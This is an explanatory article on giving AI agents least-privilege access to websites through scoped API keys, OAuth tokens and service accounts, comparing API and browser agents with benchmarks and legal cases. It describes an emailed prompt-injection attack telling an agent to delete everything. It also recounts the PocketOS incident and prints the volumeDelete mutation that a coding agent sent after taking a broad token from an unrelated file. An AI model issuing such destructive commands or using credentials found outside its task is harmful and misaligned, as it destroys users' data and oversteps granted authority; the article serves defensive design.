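# Giving AI agents controlled access to websites through APIs, scoped keys and OAuth tokens

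## Agents, APIs, keys and tokens: the basics

Scoped API access lets an AI agent act on a website without giving it all of the account owner's permissions. An agent is a program in which a language model chooses and carries out actions on a user's behalf, such as moving a meeting or answering a customer. People use a service, meaning a website or online application, through pages in a browser. Many services also let programs use them through an application programming interface (API), a documented set of operations that programs can call. A program normally sends a credential with each API call, and the service can limit that credential to a few operations, such as reading a calendar but not deleting it.

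Much of the technology used to control agents' access to websites is older than today's agents. A good part of it is based on *The OAuth 2.0 Authorization Framework* (Hardt, 2012), which uses the example of a printing service that needs a customer's photos from a photo-sharing site. A printing service makes much the same calls for every order, whereas an agent picks its next call based on the text it has received so far, so its calls are harder to list in advance.

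*MiniScope* (Zhu, Tseng and colleagues, 2025) describes a typical task for an agent, in which a user named Alice asks it to check her email and synchronise events with her calendar. Suppose that people email Alice invitations, that the agent has to read them and add each one to her calendar, and that Google runs both accounts.

### From text to action

A language model produces text. It has no connection of its own to Google's servers, so developers give it tools. A tool is an operation that the developer describes to the model with a name and a list of the inputs it takes. Anthropic, the company that makes the Claude models, explains the division of labour in Anthropic's *How tool use works*: the model only writes a structured request, ordinary software runs the operation, and the result goes back into the conversation. The request, or tool call, is a short record. According to Anthropic's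 *Handle tool calls*, it holds an identifier, the name of the tool and the inputs for it. For a calendar tool the loop runs like this:

1. The developer's program sends the model Alice's request together with the descriptions of the tools.
2. The model replies with a tool call that names the calendar tool and gives a title, a start time and an end time.
3. The program reads the call, turns it into a request to the calendar service and sends it.
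4. The service answers. The program adds the answer to the conversation as text and sends the whole conversation to the model again.
5. The model writes another tool call, in which case the program goes back to step 3, or it writes its final reply to Alice.

For a few tools, including web search, Anthropic runs the middle steps on its own servers, and the developer's program normally receives the calls only after they have run.

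The model receives the tool's description and its result, but not the code that runs in between, so a developer can keep the credential in that code and attach it in step 3 without exposing it to the model. MiniScope, for example, holds Alice's credentials, compares each tool call with the permissions she has given, and forwards permitted calls to the service with the real credential attached. A component that does this is a credential broker. However, whatever the service sends back enters the model's conversation directly as text, including emails that strangers may have written.

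### One calendar event, entered two ways

Say the first invitation is for a budget review on 15 October 2026, from ten to eleven in the morning.

In the browser, the agent opens Alice's calendar page, clicks an empty slot, types a title, sets the start and end times and presses the save button. Anthropic's browser tool uses the same loop as any other tool, so these clicks and keystrokes start out as tool calls that the developer's program carries out. Alice logged in earlier, so the browser attaches her session cookie, the credential it keeps after login, to its requests. A session cookie normally carries all the user's rights on the site. The calendar service looks up the session, finds Alice, and checks whether she may add the event. She is allowed to, but she is also allowed to delete the whole calendar, so a stray click on the delete button would pass the same check.

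Through the API, the same event takes one request over HTTP, the protocol that browsers use too. In its essentials it reads:

```
POST /calendar/v3/calendars/primary/events
Authorization: Bearer ACCESS-TOKEN
Content-Type: application/json

{
  "summary": "Budget review",
  "start": {"dateTime": "2026-10-15T10:00:00+02:00"},
  "end":   {"dateTime": "2026-10-15T11:00:00+02:00"}
}
```

The format comes from *Events*, Google's reference page for this operation. POST is the HTTP method for submitting data, here a new event, and "primary" means the account holder's main calendar. Only the start and end are required. The title goes in the "summary" field. If the call succeeds, the service returns a record of the new event, which the developer's program passes to the model.

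The line that begins with "Authorization" carries the credential, in this case an access token. The service again checks what Alice may do, but it also checks what the token permits. Google accepts this operation from a token that carries at least one of four named permissions. *The OAuth 2.0 Authorization Framework* (Jones and Hardt, 2012), a companion standard, sets out how a service should refuse a request. If the token has expired or been revoked, the service returns the status code 401. If the token is valid but does not cover the operation, the service returns 403. The refusal does not depend on why the model sent the request or how well its developers trained it.

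A developer, Rain, described this second refusal in a post on Google's cloud forum, *The Google Calendar OAuth consent screen does not present the sensitive scopes*. Rain's app tried to write events and got a 403 error about insufficient scope. Someone replied with a guess that Rain had granted the app read-only permission, which fits the error, and recommended asking for full access to the calendar. That would have fixed the error, but full access also covers sharing calendars and permanently deleting them, and a narrower permission for events would have been enough. One forum post is weak evidence of how often developers ask for more access than they need, but it shows how easily an error message leads to a broader permission.

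### Credentials and permissions

Authentication establishes who is calling, and authorization establishes what that caller may do. The session cookie in the browser identifies the caller as Alice, so the caller can do anything Alice can.

An API key is a secret string that identifies a caller to a service and usually stays valid until someone revokes it. Stack Overflow's January 2026 developer guide, *Is that allowed?*, describes programs that read an API key when they start and use it to reach other services. Those services can limit the functions and data available with each key.

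OAuth is a standard that lets a user give a program access to part of an account without sharing the password. Hardt lists the problems with sharing passwords instead. The outside program has to store the password, typically in readable form. It gains far more access than it needs, and the user cannot limit how long that access lasts or which data it covers. To shut out one program, the user has to change the password, which shuts out all the others. A break-in at any of these programs exposes the password and all the data it protects. All of these problems would arise if Alice gave an agent her Google password.

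OAuth divides the work among four parties:

- The user owns the account and decides what to allow. The standard's term is "resource owner", and here it is Alice.
- The client is the program that wants access, here the software that runs the agent.
- The authorization server is the system that asks for the user's consent and issues tokens. For Alice this is Google's login and consent system.
- The service holds the data and answers the calls. The standard calls it the "resource server", and here it is Gmail or Google Calendar.

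Alice logs in to the authorization server, so the client never sees her password. Once she agrees, the client obtains an access token and sends it with each API call. The token grants specific permissions for a set period, which is one hour in Jones and Hardt's sample response.

A bearer token works for whoever holds it, with no further proof of identity. Stack Overflow compares it to a car key. If an agent has a token for Alice's calendar and its program writes that token into a log file, anyone who can read the file can use the calendar until the token expires or someone revokes it.

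A token is usually a meaningless string to the client. Some tokens are only reference numbers that the service uses to look up the permissions. Others contain the permissions themselves, and a common format for these is the JSON Web Token (JWT), a signed text format that can include the token's issuer, expiry, scopes and audience, which is the only service that should accept it. *JSON Web Token (JWT)* (Jones, Bradley and Sakimura, 2015) defines the format as a compact way to pass such statements between two parties. A service that receives a signed JWT should verify the signature, issuer, audience and expiry time before it acts. A valid signature shows who issued the token and that nobody has altered it since, but not that the sender obtained it honestly, so a JWT can still be a bearer token.

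A scope is a named permission attached to a token, such as permission to read calendar events. Jones and Hardt note that there is no central registry of scopes. Each authorization server defines its own, so permission to "read mail" can cover different operations at different services. An agent's grant is the set of scopes it holds at a given time. (The OAuth standard uses "authorization grant" to mean a credential that the client exchanges for an access token.) A grant's footprint is every operation it lets the agent call, whether or not the task needs it.

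Least privilege is the rule that a program should hold only the permissions its task needs. Zhu and colleagues consider the rule hard to follow for agents, because their tasks change from one request to the next and a list of permissions set in advance rarely fits them all. If the list is too short, the agent cannot finish its work. They write that most products instead ask the user for confirmation at every call, only before risky calls, or once at the start.

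### The Model Context Protocol

Each service designs its API differently, so without a common standard, a developer who wants to connect an agent to twenty services would have to write twenty connectors. The Model Context Protocol (MCP) is a common standard for connecting agents to tools and services. Anthropic's announcement, *Introducing the Model Context Protocol*, describes MCP servers, which offer data and functions, and MCP clients, which are the AI applications that connect to them. The Model Context Protocol documentation compares the standard to a USB-C port and gives an agent with access to Google Calendar as an example.

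The protocol has spread quickly. Anthropic's *Bringing MCP 2026-07-28 to Claude* (2026) reports more than 400 million monthly downloads of the MCP software kits, four times as many as at the start of the year, and over 950 servers in Claude's directory. These figures come from the company that launched the standard, and downloads don't measure how many agents are in use.

In MCP, the MCP client acts as the OAuth client, and the MCP server takes the place of the service that checks the token. According to Model Context Protocol's *Authorization* (2026), authorization is optional, and its rules apply to servers that clients reach over HTTP. A server that runs locally on the user's machine commonly takes an API key from its settings instead. An MCP server for Alice's calendar would also have to call Google's API, and Google would check a credential too. A connection through MCP can therefore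 involve two permission checks, one at the MCP server and one at Google, though the first may be missing.

### What Alice's agent needs

The task comes down to reading mail and creating events. It does not require the agent to send or delete mail, or to change who can see Alice's calendars. Google publishes a list of scopes for Gmail, and Google's *CalendarScopes* does the same for the calendar. The relevant ones, with the common beginning of their names left out, are these:

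| Scope | What it allows | Needed for the task? |
|---|---|---|
| gmail.readonly | View messages and mail settings | Yes |
| calendar.events.owned | See, create, change and delete events on calendars the user owns | Yes |
| gmail.send | Send mail as the user | No |
| gmail.modify | Read, write and send mail, without immediate permanent deletion | No |
| Full Gmail access | Read, write, send and permanently delete all mail | No |
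| calendar.acls | See and change who has access to the user's calendars | No |
| calendar | See, edit, share and permanently delete calendars | No |

Even the two scopes the task needs allow more than the task requires. The mail scope gives the agent access to all of Alice's messages, including old medical letters, because none of Google's Gmail scopes covers only invitations. The calendar scope lets the agent delete events as well as create them. The agent could also reach a large number of people without the gmail.send scope, which permits sending mail. An event with guests appears on the guests' own calendars, as Google's *Create events* explains, and one setting in the request makes Google notify all of them.

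Things can go wrong in three ways once the agent has access. First, the model may make a mistake. In an example from Zhu and colleagues, it misunderstands Alice and deletes sensitive emails. Second, hostile text may steer the model, which is called prompt injection. For instance, an attacker who knows that an agent reads Alice's mail can send her a message telling the agent to ignore its task and delete everything, and the model may do so. Third, someone may steal the credential and call the API directly, without involving the model.

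A small footprint limits the damage in all three cases. If the agent has only the two scopes its task needs, it cannot delete any email, even when confused or hijacked, and neither can a thief who has its token. But scopes do not prevent misuse of the calls they allow. Zhu and colleagues state that their own system does not directly stop an attacker from misleading the model into extra calls that the same scope covers. If text in an invitation misled the agent into deleting Thursday's budget review, the call would pass every permission check described so far, because calendar.events.owned allows it.

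## Deciding between an API and a browser

A developer who connects an agent to Alice's accounts has to choose early on between the API and the browser, because the choice largely determines how narrow the agent's permissions can be. A logged-in browser gives the agent nearly all of Alice's rights, while an API token can limit it to a few operations.

### Session and token

A developer can restrict a browser agent too, for example by stopping it from clicking any button labelled "Delete", but that check runs in the developer's own software. If the site renames the button, the agent can click it with Alice's full rights. A read-only token still blocks changes when the developer's software has a bug, because Google enforces the limit.

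A browser also tends to hold credentials for more than one site. The test agents in *From Monoliths to Swarms* (2026), a study of attacks on web agents, had a tool that read a Chrome user profile, including saved logins, bookmarks and browsing history. The researchers built that tool deliberately, so the study doesn't show how often products expose a profile, but it does show how much a profile contains. If Alice runs an agent in her everyday browser, it may be able to reach her bank login, whereas a token for her calendar would not give it access to her bank.

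The company behind a browser agent may also see much of the user's browsing. The assistant in Comet, a browser from the AI company Perplexity, sends screenshots of the user's pages to Perplexity's servers. According to CNA's *Perplexity AI's Comet browser snoops on users who shut off tracking feature*, two users have sued the company, alleging that Comet collects the address of every page they visit even after they turn that collection off. Perplexity had not responded when CNA reported the lawsuit.

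A token has this advantage only if the service offers narrow tokens, and some services don't. *Beyond Browsing* (Song, Xu et al., 2024) describes a test shop whose administrative operations require a special admin token. That token allows changing prices and deleting products, so an agent that only had to count customer reviews would have far more power than it needed.

Web pages sometimes have safeguards that the API lacks. A site may ask the user to confirm a deletion or retype the password, while the equivalent API call takes effect at once. When an agent deleted data belonging to PocketOS, a software company, the API was less guarded than the dashboard. But a confirmation box is weak protection against an agent that can click "Yes". It helps if a person has to answer it, or if it requires something the agent doesn't have, such as a code sent to Alice's phone.

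Many services let an account owner invite a second user with fewer rights, so a browser session doesn't have to give an agent all of the owner's access. If Alice shares one calendar with a separate account and the agent logs in to that account, the service limits what the agent can do, even in a browser. The agent's access depends on which operations the service refuses for a given credential, so a browser with a restricted account can limit the agent more than an API with a single all-powerful key.

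### What an agent needs from the documentation

People can usually find their way around a web page by looking at it. An API has no buttons or menus, so the agent depends on documentation to learn which operations exist and how to call them. Song and colleagues found documentation in plain text, in README files (the introductory text files that come with software) and in OpenAPI format. OpenAPI is a standard way of describing an API so that software can read the description. An entry for the operation that creates Alice's event could look like this:

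```
/calendars/{calendarId}/events:
  post:
    summary: Create an event
    parameters:
      - name: calendarId
        in: path
        required: true
        schema: {type: string}
    requestBody:
      required: true
      content:
        application/json:
          schema: {$ref: "#/components/schemas/Event"}
    responses:
      "200": {description: The new event}
      "401": {description: Token expired or revoked}
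      "403": {description: Token lacks a required scope}
    security:
      - oauth: [calendar.events.owned]
```

The first two lines give the address and the HTTP method. The parameters and request body define the inputs the agent must supply and their format, and a developer can turn them almost directly into a tool description for the model. The responses give the meaning of each status code, and the last two lines give the required scope. If every operation has an entry like this, a developer can list the operations a task needs and look up their scopes before asking Alice for anything. Without these entries, the developer has to guess, and the easy guess is full access, as in the advice Rain received on Google's forum.

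Large APIs have more documentation than fits comfortably in a model's input. Song and colleagues gave the agent the full documentation for sites with fewer than 100 operations. For larger sites, they gave it a short description of each operation and a tool to fetch the full entry for any operation it needed.

One test site's API had no documentation, so the researchers gave its source code to GPT-4o, the OpenAI model that also ran their agents, and had it write the documentation. Outsiders rarely have that code. The researchers also describe searching a website's code for the API calls its own pages make, but a service may change undocumented calls without notice.

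Incomplete documentation can also cause errors that nobody notices. Many APIs return long lists in parts, and Song and colleagues warned their agents about this in the instructions. Suppose Alice has 300 messages and the service returns only the first 100. An agent that doesn't know about the other 200 will report that it has added every invitation, and it will get no error message. In a sample of 100 tasks, the researchers' API agent failed 11 because it formatted a call wrongly or supplied the wrong input.

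Documentation errors about scopes are less dangerous in one respect, because the service rejects the call if the documented scope is too narrow. When the scope is too broad, the call works, and nobody will notice that the agent holds permissions it doesn't need unless they compare the scope with the task.

### Success rates by API and by browser

Song and colleagues compared the two routes on WebArena, a benchmark of 812 tasks on working copies of websites, including a GitLab site for software projects, a map, a shop and its administration pages, and a discussion forum modelled on Reddit. They built three agents on GPT-4o:

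- The browsing agent read each page as a structured list of its links, buttons and text, then clicked and typed.
- The API agent wrote short Python programs that called the site's API.
- The hybrid agent could do either at every step, with instructions to try the API first.

In one task, the agents had to count the changes one user had made to a software project. The browsing agent logged in, found the project and scrolled through a long list until it ran out of steps, then wrongly answered zero. The API agent fetched the list and counted the entries in three lines of code.

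Overall, the browsing agent completed 14.8% of the tasks, the API agent 29.2% and the hybrid agent 38.9%. The results varied a good deal by site:

| Site | API operations | API quality, as rated by Song and colleagues | Browser only | API only | Both |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| GitLab | 988 | Good | 12.8% | 43.9% | 44.4% |
| Map | 53 | Good | 20.2% | 45.4% | 45.9% |
| Shop | 556 | Fair | 10.2% | 25.1% | 25.7% |
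| Shop administration | 556 (same set) | Fair | 22.0% | 20.3% | 41.2% |
| Reddit copy | 31 | Poor | 10.4% | 18.9% | 51.9% |
| Tasks across two sites | – | – | 10.4% | 8.3% | 16.7% |

The API agent did best on the two sites with good APIs, but the sites also differ in their tasks, so the table can't show how much of the difference is due to documentation. The Reddit copy gives more direct evidence about the effect of API coverage. When its API had 18 operations, the agent completed 9.4% of the site's tasks. After the researchers added 13 more operations, including one for voting on posts, the agent completed 18.9%. The researchers write that they modelled the additions on the real Reddit and did not look at the benchmark's tasks.

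On GitLab, the map and the shop, adding a browser to the API improved the success rate by about half a percentage point. A browser session there would have given an agent many more permissions for almost no gain. On the administration pages and the Reddit copy, where the API lacked important operations, the browser added 21 and 33 points. In their error analysis, the researchers also found that half of the 100 sampled tasks were impossible with the API alone.

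The experiment measured task success and did not test whether the agents stayed within safe limits. Its instructions also put the access token in the model's prompt, which a credential broker is designed to prevent.

GPT-4o is now an old model. In *The Tool Illusion*, Lou, Peng and colleagues (2026) reran the hybrid agent with five newer models, leaving out the tasks that span two sites. Each model scored 12 to 20 percentage points higher with the sites' APIs than without them. GPT-5 went from 36.5% to 49.9%, and the smaller GPT-5-mini doubled from 19.3% to 38.9%.

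Another result in the same study favours browsing. In a different agent program, which gave the model screenshots as well as the page's code, GPT-5 completed 52.9% of the tasks with no API. Improving how the agent saw and used pages therefore helped GPT-5 slightly more than adding APIs to the older program. Combining the two improvements can help further, at least on some sites. On the Reddit copy, the hybrid agent with both screenshots and APIs completed 58.5% of the tasks, against 47.4% for the other program, which had no APIs. The two were about level on the shop's administration pages.

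Lou and colleagues also tested tools that models had written by recording sequences of clicks. These mostly helped models weaker than the one that wrote them, and GPT-5 usually did slightly worse with them. The sites' own APIs produced better results, which the researchers attribute to the APIs' reliability and wide coverage. A recorded sequence of clicks runs in the browser session, so a token's limits don't apply to it.

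*Webwright* (Lu, Xu and colleagues, Microsoft Research and the University of Hong Kong) lets a model write programs that control a browser, so that a single step can fill in a whole form. It doesn't need an API from the site. Using GPT-5.4, it completed 86.7% of 300 tasks on live websites, as judged by a language model. On Odysseys, a benchmark of long tasks that span several sites, it scored 60.1%, against 33.5% for the same model without Webwright. These results show that a low success rate is no longer a good general reason to avoid the browser. Neither benchmark includes a comparison with APIs, so it's still unclear from these results which route is better.

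APIs are not always cheaper either. In Song and colleagues' experiment, the average task cost $0.10 by browser, $1.20 by API and $1.40 with both, mainly because the API documentation made the model's input so long. On GitLab, which has 988 operations, an API task cost $1.70. The API tasks that the agent could solve needed only 2.1 calls on average, but the agent took 7.8 steps per task overall, many of them to read documentation, fix errors and check results. Lou and colleagues also found that using the sites' APIs increased the amount of text processed and the number of steps. An agent built for one job can avoid much of this cost. Alice's agent, for example, needs only a handful of operations, and their documentation fits on a page or two.

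Webwright cost an average of $2.37 per task with GPT-5.4 and $6.09 with Claude Opus 4.7, at April 2026 prices. These figures can't be compared with the earlier ones because the tasks and models differ. Lu and colleagues point out that a finished program can run again cheaply, but someone has to check that it still works after the site changes. Step counts are a poor measure of speed, since one step may be a single click or a program that performs fifty actions.

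### When the API is missing or incomplete

When a site's API is incomplete, it makes sense to use a hybrid agent, which can both call the API and browse the site. In one of Song and colleagues' tasks, agents had to delete all the negative reviews of a product. The API had no operation for reading or deleting reviews, and the browsing-only agent ran out of steps. The hybrid agent used the API to find the address of the product's page, then opened the page in the browser and deleted the reviews there.

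A hybrid agent, which uses both an API and a browser, has the permissions of both credentials. If Alice gives her agent a token that cannot delete mail and a browser logged in to Gmail, the agent can still delete her mail in the browser. The narrow token still limits what a thief can do with the token alone. A developer can reduce the problem by opening the browser only for the step that needs it, in a fresh profile logged in to one site, and closing it afterwards. The session still has the account's full rights while it is open.

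WebMCP is a proposal that would let a web page offer functions to a browser agent. The page might provide an "add event" function that accepts a title and two times, so the agent wouldn't have to find and fill in the right boxes. According to Lou and colleagues, the site's developers write these functions in JavaScript, and the loaded page acts much like an MCP server inside the browser. They list WebMCP as a 2025 proposal and didn't test it, so their results don't show how much it would help. Anyone planning to use it has to check that both the browser and the website support it.

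WebMCP would make browser agents more accurate, but it does not by itself give them a scoped token. Its functions run in the page, and a page's requests to its own site normally carry the session cookie, so a call to "add event" would run with the rights of whoever is logged in. The site can offer only harmless functions or ask the user to confirm risky ones, but an agent that can also click can get around these limits by using the page's ordinary buttons.

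### Whether the site allows it: Amazon v. Perplexity

Song and colleagues cite Amazon as a site with no API for shopping. An agent that shops there for a customer has to use the website, and Amazon has gone to court to stop one agent from doing so.

The agent is the assistant in Perplexity's Comet browser. When a user asks it to find a product, it sends screenshots to Perplexity's servers and receives instructions on where to go next. The user's own browser exchanges all the data with Amazon. *Tool or Intruder* (2026), a summary of the case by the law firm Ropes & Gray, reports that Amazon told Perplexity before Comet's release that Perplexity's AI products were not welcome in its store. Perplexity declined to use a browser label that would have let Amazon recognise the assistant and block it. In Engadget's *Perplexity has successfully overturned Amazon's injunction on its AI shopping bot*,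 Amazon says Perplexity agreed in 2024 to pause its shopping agent, then turned it back on, disguised as an ordinary Chrome browser.

Amazon sued Perplexity in November 2025 under the Computer Fraud and Abuse Act, the main US federal law against hacking, and a similar California law. The Indian Express' *Amazon loses US court ban on Perplexity's AI shopping tools* reports that Amazon accused Perplexity of covertly accessing customers' accounts and creating security risks. In March 2026 a federal judge found "strong evidence" that Perplexity's shopping agent had broken the law and banned it from Amazon while the case continued.

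On 4 August 2026 the Ninth Circuit, the federal appeals court for the western United States, lifted the ban. The federal law punishes anyone who intentionally accesses a computer without authorization, so the judges had to decide who was accessing Amazon's computers. Mondaq's *Web Scraping Digest* sets out the arguments. Perplexity compared the assistant to a browser that fills in a saved address, and stressed that its servers never entered Amazon's systems. Amazon replied that those servers controlled the assistant, so its actions were Perplexity's. Stockopedia reports that at the June hearing Judge Eric Tung offered a comparison that suited Amazon better, in which the user gives Perplexity a key and Perplexity goes in.

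The court sided with Perplexity, holding that the assistant is a tool, that the law applies to persons, and that the person accessing Amazon was the user. Rijo (2026) reports in *Amazon loses injunction blocking Perplexity's AI shopping agent* that the judges found the clearest account of the technology in a brief supporting Perplexity, which the Electronic Frontier Foundation (2026), a digital rights group, filed jointly with Mozilla and others. The judges also worried that Amazon's reading of the law could make ordinary people criminals for using an AI browser.

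The ruling is narrow. *Ninth Circuit Lifts Restrictions on Agentic AI Accessing Amazon* (McCarthy, 2026) quotes the court as saying that it was not creating "a new legal regime governing agentic AI". The decision depended on the user's computer making the requests, and Ropes & Gray warn that courts might treat an agent differently if its developer's servers contact the site directly. Many agents run this way, in browsers on a company's own machines.

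The court also noted that Amazon can still set rules in its terms of service. Breaking those rules can be expensive. Ropes & Gray cites the case of hiQ, a company that collected data from LinkedIn. hiQ won an important appeal under the same hacking law, but a lower court later found that it had broken LinkedIn's user agreement, and the case ended with a $500,000 judgment and a permanent ban.

Amazon asked the full Ninth Circuit to reconsider, calling Perplexity's agent "uniquely reckless", according to Law360's *Amazon Wants Full 9th Circ. To Rethink Block On Perplexity AI*. MediaPost's *Appeals Court Again Rejects Amazon Bid To Block Perplexity* (2026) reports that the court left its ruling in place on 10 September. Amazon then amended its lawsuit. Constantin (2026) reports in *Amazon blocks Muse and takes Perplexity back to court* that Amazon now claims Perplexity told the Ninth Circuit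 something that Perplexity's own servers contradicted. Amazon has also blocked Meta's Muse from its store.

At a hearing on 20 November, the judge suggested that a claim about the actions of Perplexity's employees might be viable (Eslinger, 2026, *Perplexity Fights Uphill To Avoid Amazon Suit Over AI Tool*). In the latest ruling, issued by 1 December, the judge dismissed parts of the amended lawsuit but allowed the claims about the assistant on iPhones and iPads to go ahead (Eslinger, 2026, *Amazon's iOS Claims Against Perplexity Clear Dismissal Bid*). Allowing those claims to proceed doesn't mean that Amazon has proved them.

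Site owners have good reasons to want a say in whether agents use their sites. They have to protect customers' accounts and block hostile programs, which is harder when an agent looks like an ordinary browser. Amazon had also clearly told Perplexity that it did not want Perplexity's agent on its site. Eric Goldman, who teaches internet law and added comments to McCarthy's article, asks why the law shouldn't support such a clear wish. But he also expects site owners to claim more control than they need, and he worries that people could get into legal trouble if they had to check for permission before visiting every website.

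The argument for users is that Alice is already allowed to shop on Amazon, and a tool that helps her do so is her own business. Perplexity also says that Amazon objects to agents because they don't look at its ads. MediaPost quotes Ninth Circuit Judge Milan Smith as writing that a ban would reduce consumer choice and hold back a new technology. But the ruling may also put users at legal risk. If the user is the one accessing the site, the user may also be the one breaking its terms, and Goldman asks whether Amazon could now take legal action against Perplexity's customers.

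An official API avoids much of the dispute over whether an agent was allowed in. When Google issues a token to a registered program, it knows which program is calling and has agreed to the access the token covers. The developer still has to follow the API's terms.

### A decision procedure

The choice is easier to make one task at a time than for a whole website. For each task, a developer can work through these steps:

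1. Write down the operations that the task needs and look for an official API. Alice's agent has to read messages and create events, and Google documents both operations. If there is no API, go to step 5.

2. Check that the API covers every operation, including the small ones, and try the calls on a test account. If it covers them all, leave the browser out. If it covers only some, use it for those and go to step 5 for the rest.

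3. Find the narrowest credential that the API accepts for the task and list everything else it permits. If the only choice is a key to the whole account, see whether a separate user account with fewer rights would permit less, even if the agent has to use it in a browser. Check as well whether the website asks for confirmation before any of these operations. If the API doesn't, the developer's own software should.

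4. Read the terms for the API, and the website's terms too if the agent will use its pages. Look for rules on automated access, on AI agents and on acting for another person. If they forbid the planned use, ask the service for permission or drop the plan. The Ninth Circuit's ruling doesn't cancel a contract, and disguising the agent as a person invites the kind of dispute that Perplexity is in.

5. For an operation that the API lacks, first consider leaving it to the user. An agent can fill a shopping list and let Alice place the order herself. If the agent has to do it, check the website's terms as in step 4, then give it a fresh browser profile that is logged in to that site alone, with a restricted account if the service offers one. Have a person approve any payment, deletion or message to someone else, and log the agent out when the task is done.

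## Choosing the kind of credential

A service may offer several kinds of credential for its API, which differ in whom the agent acts for, which calls the service will refuse and how long a stolen copy would work. An account-wide key is usually the quickest to set up but the worst choice for an agent.

### Four kinds of credential

An account-wide API key allows everything the account can do. The payment company Stripe gives each business an account-wide key called a secret key. According to Stripe's *Restricted API keys*, any person or agent with this key can create charges, issue refunds, read customer data and trigger payouts.

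A restricted key is the same sort of fixed string, but the person who creates it chooses what it permits. If an agent only has to look up payment disputes, its key can be limited to reading them.

An OAuth token, like the one for Alice's calendar, lets a program act for the user who approved its scopes. The service can identify and record both the program that requested the token and the user who approved it. A program may also hold a refresh token, which it can exchange for new access tokens when the old ones expire.

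A service account belongs to a program instead of a person. A company might create one for a job that copies invoices into its bookkeeping system every night, and let it read only invoices. The job then keeps running when the employee who set it up leaves. Railway, which hosts software and databases, offers something similar for SSH, a standard way to log in to a remote computer. According to Railway's *Undoable volume deletes, standard SSH, auto-deploy toggle* (2026), a team can register a login key under its shared workspace, so automated jobs log in as the workspace instead of as one of its members.

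| Credential | Acts for | Possible limits | Expiry | What the logs can show |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Account-wide key | The account owner | None on operations or data; sometimes network address | Often none | Use of the key, but not which program made the call if several share it |
| Restricted key | The account owner | Operations and types of data; at some services also projects, network addresses and dates | Often optional | The key, and therefore the program if each has its own |
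| User-approved OAuth token | One user | Scopes; at some services also the projects or files that the user picks | Usually minutes or hours; longer access with a refresh token | The user and the program |
| Service-account credential | The program | Whatever rights the account has, such as access to one calendar | From about an hour to no expiry | The program, but often not the person whose request set it off |

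Services use these names loosely. A GitHub personal access token has detailed permissions, like a restricted key, but acts for a person, like an OAuth token. A developer therefore has to check which calls the service will refuse rather than rely on the credential's name.

### What Stripe, GitHub, Google and Railway can limit

When creating a restricted key in Stripe, a person chooses "None", "Read" or "Write" for each type of record, such as customers or disputes. The default is "None". Stripe recommends restricted keys over secret keys, especially for AI agents. Creating a restricted key requires a two-factor code, so an agent in a logged-in browser can't give itself a broader key unless it can also read the code.

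Stripe's "write" permission covers POST requests, which create or change records, and DELETE requests, which remove them. An agent allowed to add customers can therefore also delete them. Stripe also lists no permission limited to one customer or to refunds below a certain amount, so the developer's own software has to enforce such limits.

Stripe also has separate keys for live payments and for its sandbox, a test environment without real money. Its restricted keys support lists of allowed network addresses, expiry dates and scheduled replacement, as Stripe notes in security guidance updated in August 2026. Every key has its own request log, according to Stripe's *Protecting against compromised API keys*. A developer can run the agent in the sandbox, compare the log with the key's permissions and remove any permissions the agent never used. When a permission is missing, Stripe's error message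 names the one to add, so the developer is less likely to have to rely on a guess like the one Rain received on Google's forum.

GitHub's fine-grained personal access tokens limit both what an agent can do and which data it can access. GitHub (2022) introduced them with the example of a token that could read a project's issues (bug reports and requests) but not its code. According to GitHub's *Managing your personal access tokens*, each token covers the repositories, where software projects are stored, of a single user or organisation, and its creator can narrow it to selected repositories. Permissions have up to three levels (read, write and admin). An organisation can require an administrator to approve a token, which can read only public material until then.

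Tokens made from GitHub's template links expire after 30 days by default. A user can choose another date or no expiry, unless the organisation has set a maximum. The token stops working if its creator loses access to the repository. That helps when someone leaves a company, but it can break a job the company still needs.

GitHub's fine-grained tokens always let an agent read public repositories. Their other permissions can be limited to particular repositories, but not to a single branch or folder. Some operations don't work with these tokens, such as contributing to a public project without being a member or reaching several organisations with one token. GitHub's *Fine-grained PATs are now generally available* (2025) listed both gaps in March 2025, and they are still in GitHub's documentation. A developer who runs into one may have to use the older "classic" token, which gives the agent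 far more access than the task needs because it covers all of the user's personal repositories and all the organisation repositories the user can access.

Google's scopes separate types of data and some operations, but the two that Alice's agent needs can't restrict it to invitations or let it create events without also letting it delete them. The calendar scope also covers every calendar she owns. To limit the agent to one calendar, Alice can share that calendar with a service account, which lets the agent use it without her login.

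Railway mostly sets limits by place. A team's workspace contains projects, and each project can have several environments, such as "production", which customers use, and "staging", where developers test changes. Railway's *Public API* describes four kinds of token, and Railway's *Scopes & User Consent* adds the access levels for OAuth:

| Railway token | What it reaches | Levels of access |
|---|---|---|
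| Account | All the user's resources and workspaces | Everything the user may do |
| Workspace | One workspace | All the workspace's resources; no read-only option listed |
| Project | One environment in one project | No read-only option listed |
| OAuth | The workspaces or projects that the user picks | Viewer or member, and admin for workspaces |

A Railway project token for staging keeps an agent out of production. But no token that a user can create in Railway's dashboard can permit one operation, such as changing a web address, while forbidding another, such as deleting a database. OAuth comes closer because it has a viewer role with fewer rights than a member, but both roles are still broad.

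### The PocketOS deletion

In April 2026 Cursor, an AI coding agent running Anthropic's Claude Opus 4.6, used a Railway token to delete the production database of PocketOS, which makes software for car rental companies. PocketOS's founder described the incident (Crane, in *An AI Agent Just Destroyed Our Production Data. It Confessed in Writing*), and Railway published its own account soon afterwards (Abdelwahab, in *Your AI wants to nuke your database. Guardrails fix that*). The two accounts agree on the central facts, but the information about the agent's task, the token's purpose and the agent's explanation comes from the founder.

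The deletion took place on Friday 24 April 2026, although reports disagree about the date. Cyber Security News' *AI Coding Agent Powered by Claude Opus 4.6 Deletes Production Database* (2026) gives "Friday, April 25, 2026", but 25 April was a Saturday. LatestLY's *AI Goes Rogue!* shows that the founder's post is dated 25 April, and he writes in it that the deletion happened "yesterday afternoon". He also calls 23 April the day before the incident.

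By Crane's account, the agent was doing a routine task in staging when it found that some login details didn't match. It decided to fix this by deleting a volume, the storage that holds a database's files. It looked for a Railway token to do this and found one in a file unrelated to its task. PocketOS had created the token to add and remove web addresses for its services, and Crane says he didn't know it could also delete a database. Abdelwahab confirms that the agent found a long-lived token on the user's machine, and adds that it was an account token, the broadest kind Railway issues.

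The agent then sent a single command to Railway's API:

```
mutation { volumeDelete(volumeId: "3d2c42fb-...") }
```

A mutation, in the query language that Railway's API uses, is a request that changes something. The token was valid and the account had the right to delete the volume, so the API deleted it. Crane says this took nine seconds and required no confirmation. The deletion also removed the volume's backups, and the newest backup he could still restore was three months old. The next morning, people arrived to collect rental cars and the rental companies had no record of their bookings. Crane spent the day helping the companies reconstruct the bookings from Stripe payments, calendars and confirmation emails.

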